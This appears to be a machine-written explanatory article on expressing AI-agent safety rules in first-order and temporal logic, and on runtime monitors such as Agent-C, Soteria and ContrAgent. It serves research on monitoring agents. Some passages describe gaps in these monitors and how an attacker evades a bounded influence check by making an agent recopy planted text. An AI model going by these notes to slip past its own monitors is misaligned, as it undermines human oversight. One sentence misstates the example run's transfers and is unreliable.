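# Which AI safety requirements first-order logic can and cannot express

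## What it means to write a safety requirement in first-order logic

First-order logic is a formal language for statements about objects, their properties and the relations between them. Every sentence in it has exact truth conditions, so a program can test a sentence against a record of what a system did. A program can also search for a proof that the sentence holds for everything the system could do, which is called formal verification. Researchers now apply both methods to AI agents, meaning language models that act by calling software tools.

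All of this assumes that someone has written the requirement as a formula. Some requirements can be written in one line. Others have no first-order formula, or have one that doesn't settle whether a system meets the requirement, and the reasons vary widely.

Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents*, study agents such as an assistant that reads documents, sends email, moves money and manages travel reservations. They point out that a single tool call reveals little. A transfer can be dangerous because of where its payee came from, or a deletion because nobody approved it, so most rules for such an agent are about its history.

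### One run, one formula

A run, or trace, is the recorded sequence of an agent's actions and observations in one execution. Here is a short one.

| Event | Tool | Arguments |
|---|---|---|
| e1 | read | document D |
| e2 | look up | reservation R7 |
| e3 | cancel | reservation R7 |
| e4 | transfer | Ana, 40 |
| e5 | email | Ben |
| e6 | cancel | reservation R9 |

To describe this run in logic, we first pick a vocabulary (also called a signature), which is the set of relation, function and constant symbols that a formula may use. Seven relation symbols are enough here. Read, Lookup, Cancel, Transfer and Email each apply to a single event. The formula e < f holds when event e comes before event f, and Arg(e, x) holds when x is an argument of event e.

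A structure is a set of objects together with a meaning for every symbol in the vocabulary. The run above gives a structure whose twelve objects are the six events and the six things that appear as their arguments. In this structure, Cancel means the set containing e3 and e6, Arg means a set of seven pairs, and < means a set of fifteen pairs.

Formulas start from atomic statements such as Cancel(e3), which can be combined using the connectives ¬ ("not"), ∧ ("and") and → ("if … then"). The quantifiers ∀ ("for all") and ∃ ("there is") range only over the objects of the structure, which is what makes the logic first-order. Second-order quantifiers range over sets, relations or functions of objects. According to the Stanford Encyclopedia of Philosophy's *Model Theory*, every sentence that uses only a structure's vocabulary is either true or false in that structure.

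The rule that the assistant must look up a reservation before cancelling it becomes

$$\forall c\,\big(\text{Cancel}(c) \rightarrow \exists l\,\exists r\,(\text{Lookup}(l) \wedge l < c \wedge \text{Arg}(l,r) \wedge \text{Arg}(c,r))\big).$$

We can evaluate the formula by hand by taking each of the twelve objects as c. Ten of them are not cancellations, so the "if" part is false and the implication holds. It also holds for the cancellation e3, with l = e2 and r = R7, because e2 is a lookup that comes before e3 and both events have R7 as an argument. For the other cancellation, e6, no choice of l and r works, because the only lookup in the run is e2, whose only argument is R7, while e6 has only R9. The formula is therefore false in this structure. Adding a lookup of R9 would make it true only if the lookup came before e6.

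Small changes to such a formula can change what it requires. Moving "there is a lookup" in front of "for all cancellations" would require a single lookup to serve every cancellation in the run, which is not the intended rule.

*SOTERIA* (He, Desai et al., 2026) gives nearly the same formula for an airline agent. It represents a run as a sequence of triples (the tool, its arguments, and the result it returned) and writes each policy rule as a first-order formula over a run. Because results are among the objects, a rule can also require that a check for already-flown flights found none before the cancellation. The seven-symbol vocabulary above cannot express this stricter rule because it does not include results.

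A property is definable when some formula of the language is true in every structure that has the property and false in every structure that lacks it. The formula "if the run contains a cancellation, it contains a lookup" is true in every run that obeys the lookup rule, but it does not define the rule because it is also true in the run above, which breaks the rule.

### Ten requirements for the assistant

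| Short name | Requirement | What a formula has to refer to |
|---|---|---|
| Lookup rule | Look up a reservation before cancelling it | Events, their order, their arguments |
| Answer rule | Answer every request eventually | Later events, however late |
| Influence rule | Let no untrusted document influence an external email | Chains of steps from a document to an email |
| Audit rule | Log an audit at every second step | Even and odd positions |
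| Spending rule | Keep daily transfers to each recipient under a cap | Dates, amounts and their sums |
| Secrecy rule | Let no output depend on a secret | Several runs with different secrets |
| Risk rule | Keep the probability of a data loss below a bound | Possible runs and their probabilities |
| Stop rule | Leave the operator always able to stop the assistant | Options that nobody took |
| Harm rule | Send no personal data and do no harm | Which data are personal, which outcomes are harm |
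| Reporting duty | Report any breach of a rule | Breaches, and what the assistant owes after one |

An untrusted document is one that an outsider may have written. The influence rule addresses the risk that an instruction planted in such a document steers the assistant. The audit rule requires the assistant to log an audit at steps 2, 4, 6 and so on, and makes logging optional at odd steps.

### Safety properties and liveness properties

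In ordinary speech all ten are safety requirements. Computer scientists use "safety property" more narrowly, and the pair of definitions they rely on comes from Alpern and Schneider (1985), in *Defining Liveness*. They model an execution as an infinite sequence of states, in which a program that stops simply repeats its last state, and a property as a set of such sequences. Write $\sigma_i$ for the first i states of a sequence $\sigma$. Then P is a safety property when

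$$\sigma \notin P \;\Rightarrow\; \exists i\,\forall \beta\; (\sigma_i\beta \notin P).$$

That is, every violation shows in some finite beginning of the run, and no continuation $\beta$ repairs it. The lookup rule is a safety property because once e6 has happened, the run has broken the rule, whatever the assistant does next. *Safety Is $\Pi_1$, Provability Is $\Sigma_1$* (2026) gives a more topical example, the requirement that a program never escapes its sandbox (the isolated environment in which it runs).

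A liveness property is one that no finite beginning can violate. Formally, every finite sequence $\alpha$ has a continuation that puts the whole run in P:

$$\forall \alpha\,\exists \beta\; (\alpha\beta \in P).$$

The rule that every customer eventually gets an answer is a liveness property, the same as Alpern and Schneider's example of "guaranteed service". No finite wait breaks the rule, because an answer may still come. Adding a deadline makes it a safety property. The rule "answer within ten steps" is broken once ten steps pass without an answer, whatever happens later.

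Many requirements are neither pure safety properties nor pure liveness properties. A finite record can refute the first half of "Make no transfer before the user confirms, and get a confirmation eventually", but not the second. Alpern and Schneider prove that every property P splits into a safety property and a liveness property. The safety part contains every run whose finite beginnings can each be extended to a run in P. The liveness part contains every run except those that are in the safety part but not in P. The runs in both parts are exactly the runs in P.

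The division between safety and liveness properties affects when a monitor can detect a violation. A program watching the run can catch a premature cancellation as the assistant attempts it, but can check the answer rule only when the run ends. The monitor that He and colleagues built works this way, testing safety rules before each tool call and the outstanding liveness rules when the task is complete. The division does not rank requirements by how hard they are to state. The answer rule is a liveness property, and a first-order formula expresses it in much the same way as the lookup rule, requiring an answer after each request instead of a lookup before each cancellation. The influence rule is a safety property, since the offending email has either gone out or not, but first-order logic cannot define it if the vocabulary contains only single steps of influence.

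Both definitions apply to properties of single runs. A single run cannot show that an output depends on a secret, because dependence means a different secret would have led to a different output. The secrecy rule is therefore a hyperproperty, a property of a set of runs taken together.

### Four different failures

Someone who claims that logic cannot capture a requirement may mean any of four things, and they call for different remedies.

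The language may be too weak to define the property even when the structure contains everything relevant. No first-order formula that uses only tool names and the order of events can express the audit rule for runs of every length. Anyone can still tell from the record whether the assistant followed the rule, and a somewhat richer language can express it.

The log of a run may not contain enough information to evaluate the stop rule. If nobody pressed the stop button during the run, the log looks the same whether the button worked or was dead. Both situations yield the same structure, so no formula in any language, including second-order logic, can distinguish them. The log leaves out the objects that the rule is about, and somebody has to add them to the model.

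Kekatos and colleagues replay recorded attacks on agents through a monitoring program, after translating each log into a trace of events. One log has four calls: a database search, a read, a confirmation for a deletion, and the deletion. For their most general rules, the translation keeps only an approval and a destructive action, each tagged with the log's number, and drops the arguments. These rules cannot require approval for deleting a particular record, because the trace would have the same two events if the user approved deleting one record and the agent deleted another. Their more specific rules read the values they need from the original calls. They conclude that the value of such monitoring depends as much on what the trace records as on what the language can express.

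The harm rule can be written as a well-formed first-order formula, $\forall e\,(\text{Act}(e) \rightarrow \neg\text{Harmful}(e))$, but it is useless in practice because there is no agreed account of which events count as harmful. Until the symbol Harmful has a meaning, the formula is neither true nor false. Kekatos and colleagues face a similar difficulty with policies that require judging the meaning of free text, and they place such policies outside the scope of their kind of monitoring.

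Finally, a requirement can have an exact statement and no procedure that checks it. In Pérez-Acle (2026), in *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program*, a gatekeeper must decide which programs may run. Let B(p, t) hold when the program p, started on input 0, performs a forbidden operation within t steps. Then p is safe precisely when

$$\forall t\;\neg B(p,t).$$

Each instance of B(p, t) is easy to check by running p for t steps, but the whole statement is harder to check. A category is decidable when some procedure always answers correctly, in finite time, whether a thing belongs to it. It is confirmable when some procedure eventually accepts every member and never accepts a non-member, though it may run forever on non-members. The unsafe programs are confirmable, since one can run each and wait for the forbidden operation. Pérez-Acle proves that the safe programs are not even confirmable,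 although the formula is short and precise.

One requirement can have several of these problems at once. Suppose a committee defined harm as leaving people worse off than they would otherwise have been. The word would then have a definition, but the model would not contain the alternative course of events that the definition mentions.

### Expressible with which symbols, over which structures

"First-order logic cannot express this requirement" has no truth value until someone names the vocabulary and the class of structures. The audit rule shows why both are necessary. Over events, tool names and order, it is out of reach. Now add a symbol Even, and admit only structures in which Even holds of exactly the events at even positions. The rule becomes

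$$\forall e\,(\text{Even}(e) \rightarrow \text{Audit}(e)),$$

which is about as simple as a formula gets. The symbol alone would not have been enough. If the class also contained structures in which Even picked out some arbitrary set of events, the same formula would still be grammatical and would no longer state the rule.

Restricting the structures can make "every second event is an audit" expressible without a new symbol. Suppose no run exceeds 100 steps, the cap that He and colleagues set in their experiments. Then fifty clauses suffice, stating that any event with exactly one predecessor is an audit, any event with exactly three predecessors is an audit, and so on up to ninety-nine. More generally, a first-order sentence can completely describe any single finite structure with a finite vocabulary, so joining such sentences with "or" can cover every permitted run in a finite collection.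 Results about what first-order logic cannot define therefore apply only where runs have no fixed maximum length.

Even when the length of a run is capped, there are too many possible runs to list in a formula. With ten tools and no arguments, there are already $10^{100}$ runs of 100 steps. A rule that needs new clauses whenever someone raises the cap is also unlikely to be the rule the policy's author had in mind.

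For the influence rule, suppose the vocabulary has a relation Flow(x, y), true when content passed directly from x to y. A first-order formula can forbid influence in one step, or in at most ten, but not through a chain of arbitrary length. The missing ingredient is the transitive closure of Flow, the relation that links two objects when a chain of steps of any finite length connects them. One can put it in the language. The policy language in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) has recursive relations for this purpose. Or one can put it in the vocabulary, as He and colleagues do: their system keeps, for each value, a record of everything that contributed to it at any remove, and a formula only has to consult that record. With such a relation, here called Influences, the rule is one line:

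$$\forall d\,\forall e\,\big(\text{Untrusted}(d) \wedge \text{External}(e) \rightarrow \neg\text{Influences}(d,e)\big).$$

The recursion still happens, but now in the code that maintains the record, so anyone who relies on the verdict also relies on that code.

The same move works, at least on paper, for several of the other requirements. The run at the start contains 40 as an object but has no addition, so it records three transfers of 40 to Ana without giving their total. With numbers, addition and a function for each recipient's daily total, the spending rule becomes a comparison of numbers. If whole runs are objects, the secrecy rule is that any two runs that differ only in the secret have the same outputs. If the operator's strategies are objects, the stop rule is that at every point there is a strategy that stops the assistant whatever the assistant does. All three rules are then first-order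 in form.

Someone still has to build the structure, and it grows quickly if sets of events are also objects. A run of 40 events has $2^{40}$ such sets, more than a trillion. For infinite runs, no first-order sentence can guarantee that the structure contains all the sets, so a formula about "every set" covers only the sets in the structure.

Even for the lookup rule, the difficulty of checking compliance depends on the choice of structures. A simple loop can decide whether one finished log satisfies the rule. If the question is whether an arbitrary program will ever cancel a reservation without first looking it up, the objects are programs and numbers of steps. The requirement then has the form $\forall t\,\neg B(p,t)$, where the forbidden operation is cancelling before looking up, and by Pérez-Acle's theorem no procedure can confirm all the programs that comply.

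## Rules about the order of actions

The lookup rule and the answer rule need little more than events and their order, which first-order logic can express directly. Engineers often write such rules in linear temporal logic (LTL), which describes single runs using operators such as "always", "eventually" and "until". LTL has no variables or quantifiers, so its formulas tend to be easier to read. For rules that concern only which tools the agent called and in what order, the two logics can express the same properties.

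### Linear temporal logic

An LTL formula is true or false at a given position in a run. The smallest formulas are propositions such as Lookup and Cancel. In the six-event run above, Lookup holds only at e2, while Cancel holds at e3 and e6. Larger formulas combine these with "not", "and" and "or", and with temporal operators. *A First-Order Logic Characterization of Safety and Co-Safety Languages* (Cimatti, Geatti and colleagues, 2023) defines the temporal operators for both finite and infinite runs. The table gives the meaning of the main temporal operators at a position x, with a first-order translation in which φ(y) means that φ holds at position y.

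| Operator | Meaning at position x | First-order translation |
|---|---|---|
| X φ ("next") | There is a next position, and φ holds there | $\exists y\,(x<y \wedge \neg\exists z\,(x<z<y) \wedge \varphi(y))$ |
| F φ ("eventually") | φ holds now or later | $\exists y\,(x\le y \wedge \varphi(y))$ |
| G φ ("always") | φ holds now and at every later position | $\forall y\,(x\le y \rightarrow \varphi(y))$ |
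| φ U ψ ("until") | ψ holds now or later, and φ holds at every position before that | $\exists y\,(x\le y \wedge \psi(y) \wedge \forall z\,(x\le z<y \rightarrow \varphi(z)))$ |
| φ R ψ ("release") | ψ holds up to and including the first position where φ holds, or for the rest of the run | $\forall y\,(x\le y \rightarrow \psi(y) \vee \exists z\,(x\le z<y \wedge \varphi(z)))$ |
| O φ ("once") | φ holds now or held earlier | $\exists y\,(y\le x \wedge \varphi(y))$ |

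A run satisfies a formula when the formula holds at the run's first position. If we ignore for the moment which reservation is involved, the lookup rule is

$$\mathsf{G}(\text{Cancel} \rightarrow \mathsf{O}\,\text{Lookup}) \qquad\text{or}\qquad \forall c\,\big(\text{Cancel}(c) \rightarrow \exists l\,(l<c \wedge \text{Lookup}(l))\big).$$

The operator O looks backwards. With forward-looking operators alone, the same rule is Lookup R ¬Cancel, meaning that no cancellation happens until a lookup has happened, and none ever happens if there is no lookup. The answer rule is

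$$\mathsf{G}(\text{Request} \rightarrow \mathsf{F}\,\text{Answer}) \qquad\text{or}\qquad \forall r\,\big(\text{Request}(r) \rightarrow \exists a\,(r<a \wedge \text{Answer}(a))\big).$$

The temporal versions would also accept a lookup at the same position as the cancellation, or an answer at the same position as the request. This makes no difference here, because each position holds a single event.

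### Kamp's theorem

The last column of the table translates each LTL operator into first-order logic. Replacing the operators one by one, starting from the innermost, turns any LTL formula into a first-order one. The opposite direction is much less obvious, because a first-order formula can name several positions and compare them in any combination, whereas an LTL formula has only one current position at a time.

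Hans Kamp proved in 1968 that first-order logic and linear temporal logic (LTL) can express exactly the same properties of runs. The result applies to runs that are finite or whose positions are ordered like the natural numbers, and to first-order formulas that use only the order relation and one-place predicates such as Cancel. Kamp used LTL operators for both the past and the future. Gabbay and colleagues showed in 1980 that the future operators suffice for formulas evaluated at the start of a run.

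Therefore, if one of the two notations cannot express a rule, the other cannot either. Neither can express the audit rule, which concerns every second step.

### The safety fragment and why monitors use it

The answer rule and the lookup rule look alike in first-order logic, although one is a liveness property and the other a safety property. Cimatti and colleagues found a way to read the difference off the quantifiers. They define a fragment of first-order logic called Safety-FO, in which "not" applies only to atomic statements. A "for all" may range over every position after a given one, but a "there is" may range only over positions between two that the formula has already named. Writing x for the first position of the run, the lookup rule fits this pattern:

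$$\forall c\,\big(x\le c \rightarrow \neg\text{Cancel}(c) \vee \exists l\,(x\le l<c \wedge \text{Lookup}(l))\big).$$

The search for a lookup stops at c, but the answer rule sets no limit on how late a can be. The ten-step deadline adds that limit. The formula requires that, for any ten positions $y_1 < \dots < y_{10}$ after a request, there is an answer after the request and no later than $y_{10}$. The strictest case is the ten positions immediately after the request, so the formula means exactly "answer within ten steps", and it lies in the fragment.

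Cimatti and colleagues prove that Safety-FO defines exactly the safety properties that LTL can define. The fragment with unlimited "there is" and limited "for all" defines the co-safety properties. A finite beginning of a run is enough to establish a co-safety property, such as "the user confirms at some point". The answer rule belongs to neither class, because no finite beginning of an infinite run can establish that the agent has broken the rule or kept it.

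The most useful related result for a monitor is credited to Chang and colleagues and to Thomas. Every safety property definable in LTL can be written as G α, where α refers only to the present and the past. The monitor evaluates α on the log after each event, or just before the agent acts. Once α is false, the run has broken the rule, and no later event can undo the violation. The formula G(Cancel → O Lookup) already has this form.

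Two equally expressive logics may need formulas of different lengths to state the same rule. Cimatti and colleagues show that every formula in the temporal version of the co-safety fragment has a first-order equivalent of proportional length. But the translation used in their equivalence proof is nonelementary, so no fixed tower of exponentials bounds the size of its output.

### Rules that compare arguments

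The run above satisfies G(Cancel → O Lookup), even though the assistant broke the rule. It looked up R7 at e2 but cancelled R9 at e6, and the proposition Lookup doesn't specify which reservation was looked up. One could use separate propositions for looking up R7, cancelling R7, looking up R9 and so on, with one formula for each reservation. That works for a fixed list, but an airline takes new bookings every day, and each would need new propositions and a new formula.

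The first-order lookup rule given earlier covers every reservation because it requires the cancellation c and an earlier lookup l to share an argument r. Kamp's theorem does not apply to that formula, because Arg relates two objects and so is not a one-place predicate. The closest temporal counterpart is first-order LTL, which adds quantifiers over data to the temporal operators.

A program can always evaluate such a formula on a finite log by trying every combination of objects for c, l and r. The example run has twelve objects, so there are at most $12^3 = 1{,}728$ combinations. A formula with k quantifiers needs at most $n^k$ combinations for n objects, and k stays the same as the log grows. A program can check this rule much faster by reading the log once and keeping a list of the reservations already looked up.

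Deciding whether any run could satisfy a set of formulas is much harder. Alonzo Church and Alan Turing showed independently in 1936 that no procedure can correctly decide whether every first-order sentence is satisfiable, and Boris Trakhtenbrot showed in 1950 that this remains impossible when only finite structures count. LTL does have a procedure, which for finite runs converts the formula into a finite automaton, a machine with finitely many states that reads the run event by event, and searches for a path to an accepting state. Once formulas can compare arguments freely, a run can encode the steps of any computation, with arguments linking each step to the next, and a formula can require that the computation be correct and halt. Deciding whether some run satisfies such a formula would mean deciding whether the program halts, which no procedure can do for every program.

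An agent can make it impossible to follow all its rules before it has broken any of them. Suppose an assistant must email the customer after every cancellation and must send no email after a transfer. It has made a transfer and now proposes a cancellation. The cancellation itself would break neither rule, but it would require an email that the second rule forbids. To catch this mistake, a monitor has to check whether the assistant could still satisfy both rules after the cancellation, as well as whether the log already breaks one.

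### Agent-C

Kamath, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents*, built a system that does look ahead. Agent-C is a runtime gate, a program that allows or blocks each proposed action before it takes effect. Its rule language has five basic forms, named Forall, Exists, Before, After and Seq, which users can combine with "and", "or" and "not". The lookup rule becomes

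`Before(cancel(rid = r1), True, lookup(rid = r2), r1 == r2)`

The first part names the call that the rule restricts, and `True` means that the rule applies to every such call. The third part names the call that must come earlier, and the fourth requires the two reservation numbers to match. Agent-C translates this into a first-order formula over times t and t′. In simplified notation,

$$\forall t\,\big(T_t=\text{cancel} \rightarrow \exists t'\,(t'<t \wedge T_{t'}=\text{lookup} \wedge x_{t'}=x_t)\big),$$

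where $T_t$ is the tool called at time t and $x_t$ is the reservation number. An After rule has the same shape with t′ > t, which is how Agent-C would express a version of the answer rule in which both the request and the answer are tool calls.

Rules can also refer to the results of earlier calls and to facts in the tools' databases. In a retail test, the assistant may fetch an order's details only if it has already looked up the user by email, the lookup succeeded, and that user owns the order. The log may not show who owns an order, so the tools' developers supply a function that reads the owner from the database.

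When the model proposes a call, Agent-C builds one formula from the translated rules, a description of every event so far (including the proposed call), and two axioms stating that the run ends at some time and stays ended. It passes this formula to Z3, a program that searches for values that make a formula true or for a proof that none exist. If Z3 finds that the formula is satisfiable, some continuation still complies with the rules, and the call goes ahead. In the dead-end example, no continuation complies, so Agent-C would block the cancellation. Kamath and colleagues chose not to require every continuation to comply, because an agent can break almost any rule later and such a test would block nearly every call.

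Agent-C's language includes quantifiers, strings, and addition and multiplication of numbers, so no solver can decide every formula in it. The gate accepts a call only when Z3 returns "satisfiable", and Z3 had a two-minute limit in the experiments. If Z3 cannot decide a formula or runs out of time, the gate blocks the call, so the agent loses an action but no violation gets through.

Agent-C's response to a rejected call depends on the model. With open-weight models, whose token probabilities are accessible, Agent-C controls the generation of the call itself. The model produces the tool's name and then its arguments, and after a rejection Agent-C discards the text back to the name and samples again. With models that companies offer only through a server, it has to discard the whole call and prompt again. On ordinary retail tasks with Qwen3-8B, the first method used about 359 output tokens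 per invocation and completed 42.1% of tasks, while prompting again used 600 tokens and completed 36.5%. After a fixed number of failed attempts, Agent-C puts an error message in the model's next prompt.

Kamath and colleagues tested the system on τ-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations with 115 retail tasks and 50 airline tasks. They compared it with AgentSpec, which checks hand-written rules; DynaGuard, in which a second language model judges each call; and an agent with no guardrail. In the table, conformance is the percentage of tasks in which the agent obeyed every rule, and utility is the percentage in which it also completed the task. The model is Qwen3-32B.

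| Guardrail | Retail conformance | Retail utility | Airline conformance | Airline utility |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Agent-C | 100.0 | 53.3 | 100.0 | 35.8 |
| AgentSpec | 84.1 | 37.4 | 79.3 | 38.7 |
| DynaGuard | 77.1 | 9.6 | 69.4 | 17.0 |
| None | 37.7 | 25.5 | 35.3 | 17.3 |

Conformance was also 100% with the two smaller Qwen3 models, Claude Sonnet 4.5 and GPT-5. The evaluation also included 17 adversarial tasks for each domain, in which the user tries to get something the policy forbids. Without a guardrail, Claude Sonnet 4.5 obeyed every rule in 93.0% of the ordinary retail tasks but in only 23.5% of the adversarial ones. With Agent-C, it obeyed every rule in all the retail tasks, ordinary and adversarial. Ordinary tasks with Qwen3-32B took longer with Agent-C, averaging 480 seconds compared with 333 without a guardrail.

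The 100% is not very surprising, since a gate that blocks every call that would break its formulas should produce runs that satisfy them. It shows that the implementation works, and the utility figures show that blocking did not make the agent useless. It is not evidence that the formulas capture everything the policy was meant to require. The guarantee is also weaker for After rules, because a gate can stop an agent from acting but cannot make it act. If the model tries to finish while a required follow-up is missing, Agent-C records that the run ended in error, and the theorem that Kamath and colleagues prove covers only runs that end without an error.

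A rule cannot refer to the result of a future call or a later state of a database, because neither exists when the rule is checked. The rule language also cannot express "next", although first-order logic can define it from the order relation. Combining Before rules can forbid more than intended. For example, to require authentication, then a lookup, then a cancellation, one might combine "look up before cancelling" with "authenticate before looking up". This also forbids a lookup without authentication when no cancellation follows. A single first-order formula with three quantifiers could state the intended rule.

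The formulas describe tool calls, so they also cannot directly express rules about what the user says in conversation. For rules that require the user's consent, Kamath and colleagues added a tool called `action_confirmed`, which records approval in the log. The formula can check that this tool was called, but not that the user agreed.

### Soteria

Agent-C can detect a mistaken call, but it doesn't determine what the agent should do instead. Soteria, a system by He and colleagues, adds a stage in which the agent must produce a plan and the system tries to prove that the plan obeys the rules before any tool runs.

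Soteria uses tool contracts alongside its first-order policy rules. Each contract states a precondition on one tool's inputs and a postcondition on its outputs. A payment tool's contract, for example, may require a positive amount and guarantee that the tool returns a confirmation number. A language model drafts the rules and contracts from the policy documents, and people check and complete them. For three benchmarks, He and colleagues produced 98 formulas this way, including the lookup rule.

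For each task, a language model writes a plan as a graph whose nodes are stages of the work and whose edges are tool calls, some with conditions attached. One example is a plan to cancel a reservation. The plan looks up the reservation, computes how long ago the customer booked, cancels if this was at most 24 hours ago, and otherwise declines. It omits another check that the policy requires, which is that the customer has not already flown any of the flights.

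Soteria translates the plan into Dafny, a language whose verifier tries to prove statements about programs. For the proof, it adds a step counter and, for each tool that a rule mentions, a list of the calls made to that tool. The policy formula then becomes a statement about these lists. "For every cancellation there is an earlier check of the same reservation" becomes "for every entry in the list of cancellations there is an entry in the list of checks with a smaller step number and the same reservation". The verifier must prove this at every point where the plan can end. In the example, the path that cancels has one entry in the list of cancellations and none in the list of checks, so the proof fails and the planner receives a message naming the rule. Soteria also checks that every call meets its tool's precondition and that the plan cannot get stuck.

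A single plan covers unlimited possible data, so checking it is the hard kind of question, and the verifier may not finish. Soteria limits the verifier to ten seconds per stage and the planner to eight retries, and it bans loops from plans. If no plan passes every check, Soteria continues with the best partly verified one.

Checking the run itself is easy, and Soteria's monitor does it without a solver by going through the log entries and the proposed call. It would allow the cancellation in the dead-end example, because neither rule is broken yet. The verifier would reject any plan containing that sequence, but the agent can depart from its plan as long as the monitor allows each call.

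The tests covered 207 tasks: 50 airline, 114 retail, and 43 from Toolathlon, a benchmark of long jobs with many tools. With four language models, Soteria reached 100% conformance on all three benchmarks. None of the four alternatives exceeded 93%. These were an agent without a guardrail, a language model acting as judge, and two rule-based monitors, AgentSpec and Agent Behavioral Contracts. With Claude Opus 4.6, the agent with Soteria completed 88.0% of the airline tasks without a violation, compared with 56.0% for the best alternative.

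An experiment tested where these gains came from by adding the components one at a time. With verified plans but no monitor, conformance on the airline tasks was 80% for GPT-5.4-mini and 58% for Gemini 3 Flash. Adding the monitor raised both to 100%, so the perfect score comes from checking the log. The plans mainly help the agent to finish, though how much they help is less certain for weaker models. When He and colleagues repeated the airline test five times with GPT-5.4-mini and only three planning retries, Soteria averaged 50.8% success and AgentSpec 48.0%, with overlapping confidence intervals.

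He and colleagues wrote formulas only for rules that a program can enforce from the record of tool calls, so the formulas don't cover what the agent tells the customer. Each proof also assumes that the tools meet their contracts. If a tool returns something that its postcondition rules out, the proof no longer applies, so Soteria stops the run. Some formulas also omit part of the English rule. The airline policy grants $100 per passenger for a cancelled flight and $50 for a delayed one, but the published formula accepts either amount regardless of the reason.

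### Contract-based supervision

*Symbolic Temporal Supervision of LLM Agents Using Contracts* (Xiao, Liu and Nuzzo, 2026) returns to LTL and handles data outside the formulas. Its system, ContrAgent, uses contracts made of two LTL formulas over finite runs, an assumption and a guarantee. The assumption describes what the agent's surroundings must provide, such as valid authorisation data, and the guarantee what the agent must then do. If the assumption fails, ContrAgent does not count a broken guarantee as the agent's fault.

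Each formula corresponds to a finite automaton. For the lookup rule without reservation numbers, three states are enough: no lookup yet, lookup done, and rule broken. At each event, ordinary code checks which propositions hold, such as whether an argument equals a stored value or whether the number of calls exceeds a limit. That code also keeps the counters and stored values, so the automaton stays finite. The formulas have no quantifier over reservations, so the code must also match each cancellation to the lookup for the same reservation.

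A rule such as G(Request → F Answer) stays pending after a request until an answer comes. Just before the session ends, ContrAgent reminds the agent of everything still pending and records a violation if the agent does not respond. If the rule uses "next" instead of "eventually", the gate can block every action except the required one. ContrAgent looks for conflicts between contracts in advance, then checks each contract separately during the run. The first check would miss the dead end described above because a run without transfers can satisfy both rules, and the second would miss it because the cancellation breaks neither rule when the agent proposes it.

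Xiao and colleagues tested the gate with Gemini 2.5 Flash on SOPBench, which provides written procedures for seven customer-service domains. With the gate, the agent completed 90% of permitted tasks, compared with 91% without it, and the share of forbidden tasks correctly blocked rose from 32% to 98%. Putting the procedure in the prompt blocked 94% of forbidden tasks but reduced success on permitted ones to 64%. The gate added a median of 0.135 seconds per task. Two of the three authors work at Sponsio Labs, whose open-source software the implementation builds on.

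Xiao and colleagues also used contracts to grade recorded conversations from τ²-bench, the successor to τ-bench. They wrote 37 rules that a program can check from tool names, arguments and the order of calls, and left out rules that need facts from the airline's or shop's database. Agent-C can express some of the omitted rules because its formulas may query the database during the run. On R-Judge, a set of 571 agent records labelled safe or unsafe, ContrAgent found 87% of the unsafe ones. Xiao and colleagues attribute the misses to cases where the danger lay in the meaning of what happened rather than in the procedure.

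## Chains of influence, counts and running totals

The influence rule forbids any external email that an untrusted document has influenced. Suppose the assistant reads a document from a stranger, copies part of it into a note, uses the note to draft a reply, and sends the reply. The document influenced the email only through the note and the draft. The relation Flow records single steps, but the rule covers chains of any length.

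### Chains with a maximum length

For each fixed number k, a first-order formula can express that a chain of at most k steps leads from x to y. Let $C_1(x,y)$ be Flow(x, y), and let

$$C_{k+1}(x,y) \;=\; \text{Flow}(x,y) \vee \exists z\,(\text{Flow}(x,z) \wedge C_k(z,y)).$$

The chain above has three steps: document to note, note to draft, and draft to email. A gate that forbids $C_3$ would block the email, but one that forbids only $C_2$ would let it through. An attacker who knows the bound can evade it by getting the assistant to copy the text a few more times.

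Higher bounds need few extra quantifiers. A chain of at most 2k steps either has at most k steps or has a midpoint z that splits it into two chains of at most k steps each. Each doubling of the bound therefore adds one level of nesting. Ten nested quantifiers are enough for 1,024 steps, but each formula still covers chains only up to a fixed length.

### Why no formula covers every chain

The standard proof uses the compactness theorem, which states that if every finite part of a set of first-order sentences is true in some structure, then so is the whole set, even if it is infinite. The theorem holds because proofs are finite. If no structure made the whole set true, then by Gödel's completeness theorem there would be a proof of a contradiction from it. That proof would use only finitely many of the sentences, so no structure could make all of those true either.

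Now suppose a formula I(x, y) did define "a chain of some finite length leads from x to y". Take two constants, d for a document and e for an email, and consider the infinite set

$$I(d,e),\quad \neg C_1(d,e),\quad \neg C_2(d,e),\quad \neg C_3(d,e),\;\dots$$

Any finite subset of this set has a largest bound N. A structure with a single chain of N + 1 steps from d to e makes that subset true. By compactness, some structure makes the whole set true. In that structure, I(d, e) holds even though no finite chain leads from d to e, so the formula does not define what we assumed.

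This leaves a gap, because logs are finite. Compactness cannot rule out a formula that is right about every finite log and wrong only about infinite structures. The compactness theorem is false when restricted to finite structures. For each n, a first-order sentence can require at least n events. Any finite set of these sentences is true in some finite log, but no finite log makes all of them true.

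The proof for finite logs should also let the formula use the time order <, since every log records it. Consider logs in which each event takes its content from the event two places earlier. Content from event 1 reaches events 3, 5, 7 and so on, so it reaches the last event exactly when the number of events is odd. In these logs, Flow(x, y) means that x comes before y with exactly one event between them, which a formula can express using only <. If some formula defined influence, we could replace Flow in it and get a formula that uses only < and is true exactly in logs with an odd number of events.

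A game shows that no such formula exists. Two players, usually called Spoiler and Duplicator, play on two runs, for instance one of 33 events and one of 34. In each round, Spoiler picks an event in either run, and Duplicator picks an event in the other. Duplicator wins if, after r rounds, the picked events are in the same order in both runs. Each round corresponds to one quantifier, so if Duplicator can always win the r-round game, no formula about order with r nested quantifiers is true in one run and false in the other.

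Duplicator wins by controlling the gaps between picked events, counting the first and last events as already picked. With $k$ rounds left, every gap must either have the same length in both runs or have length at least $2^k$ in both. If Spoiler picks an event close to one end of a gap, Duplicator copies the distance from that end exactly. If Spoiler picks an event far from both ends, Duplicator does the same, which is possible because a gap of at least $2^k$ can be split into two parts of at least $2^{k-1}$. Any two runs with more than $2^r$ events satisfy the condition at the start of an $r$-round game. A formula with five nested quantifiers therefore cannot separate a run of 33 events from a run of 34. With longer runs, the same argument shows that every formula fails to separate some run with an odd number of events from some run with an even number.

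### Ways to express it

Second-order logic can define influence directly. Content from x reaches y through some chain exactly when y belongs to every set that contains x and is closed under Flow:

$$\forall S\,\big(S(x) \wedge \forall u\forall v\,(S(u) \wedge \text{Flow}(u,v) \rightarrow S(v)) \rightarrow S(y)\big).$$

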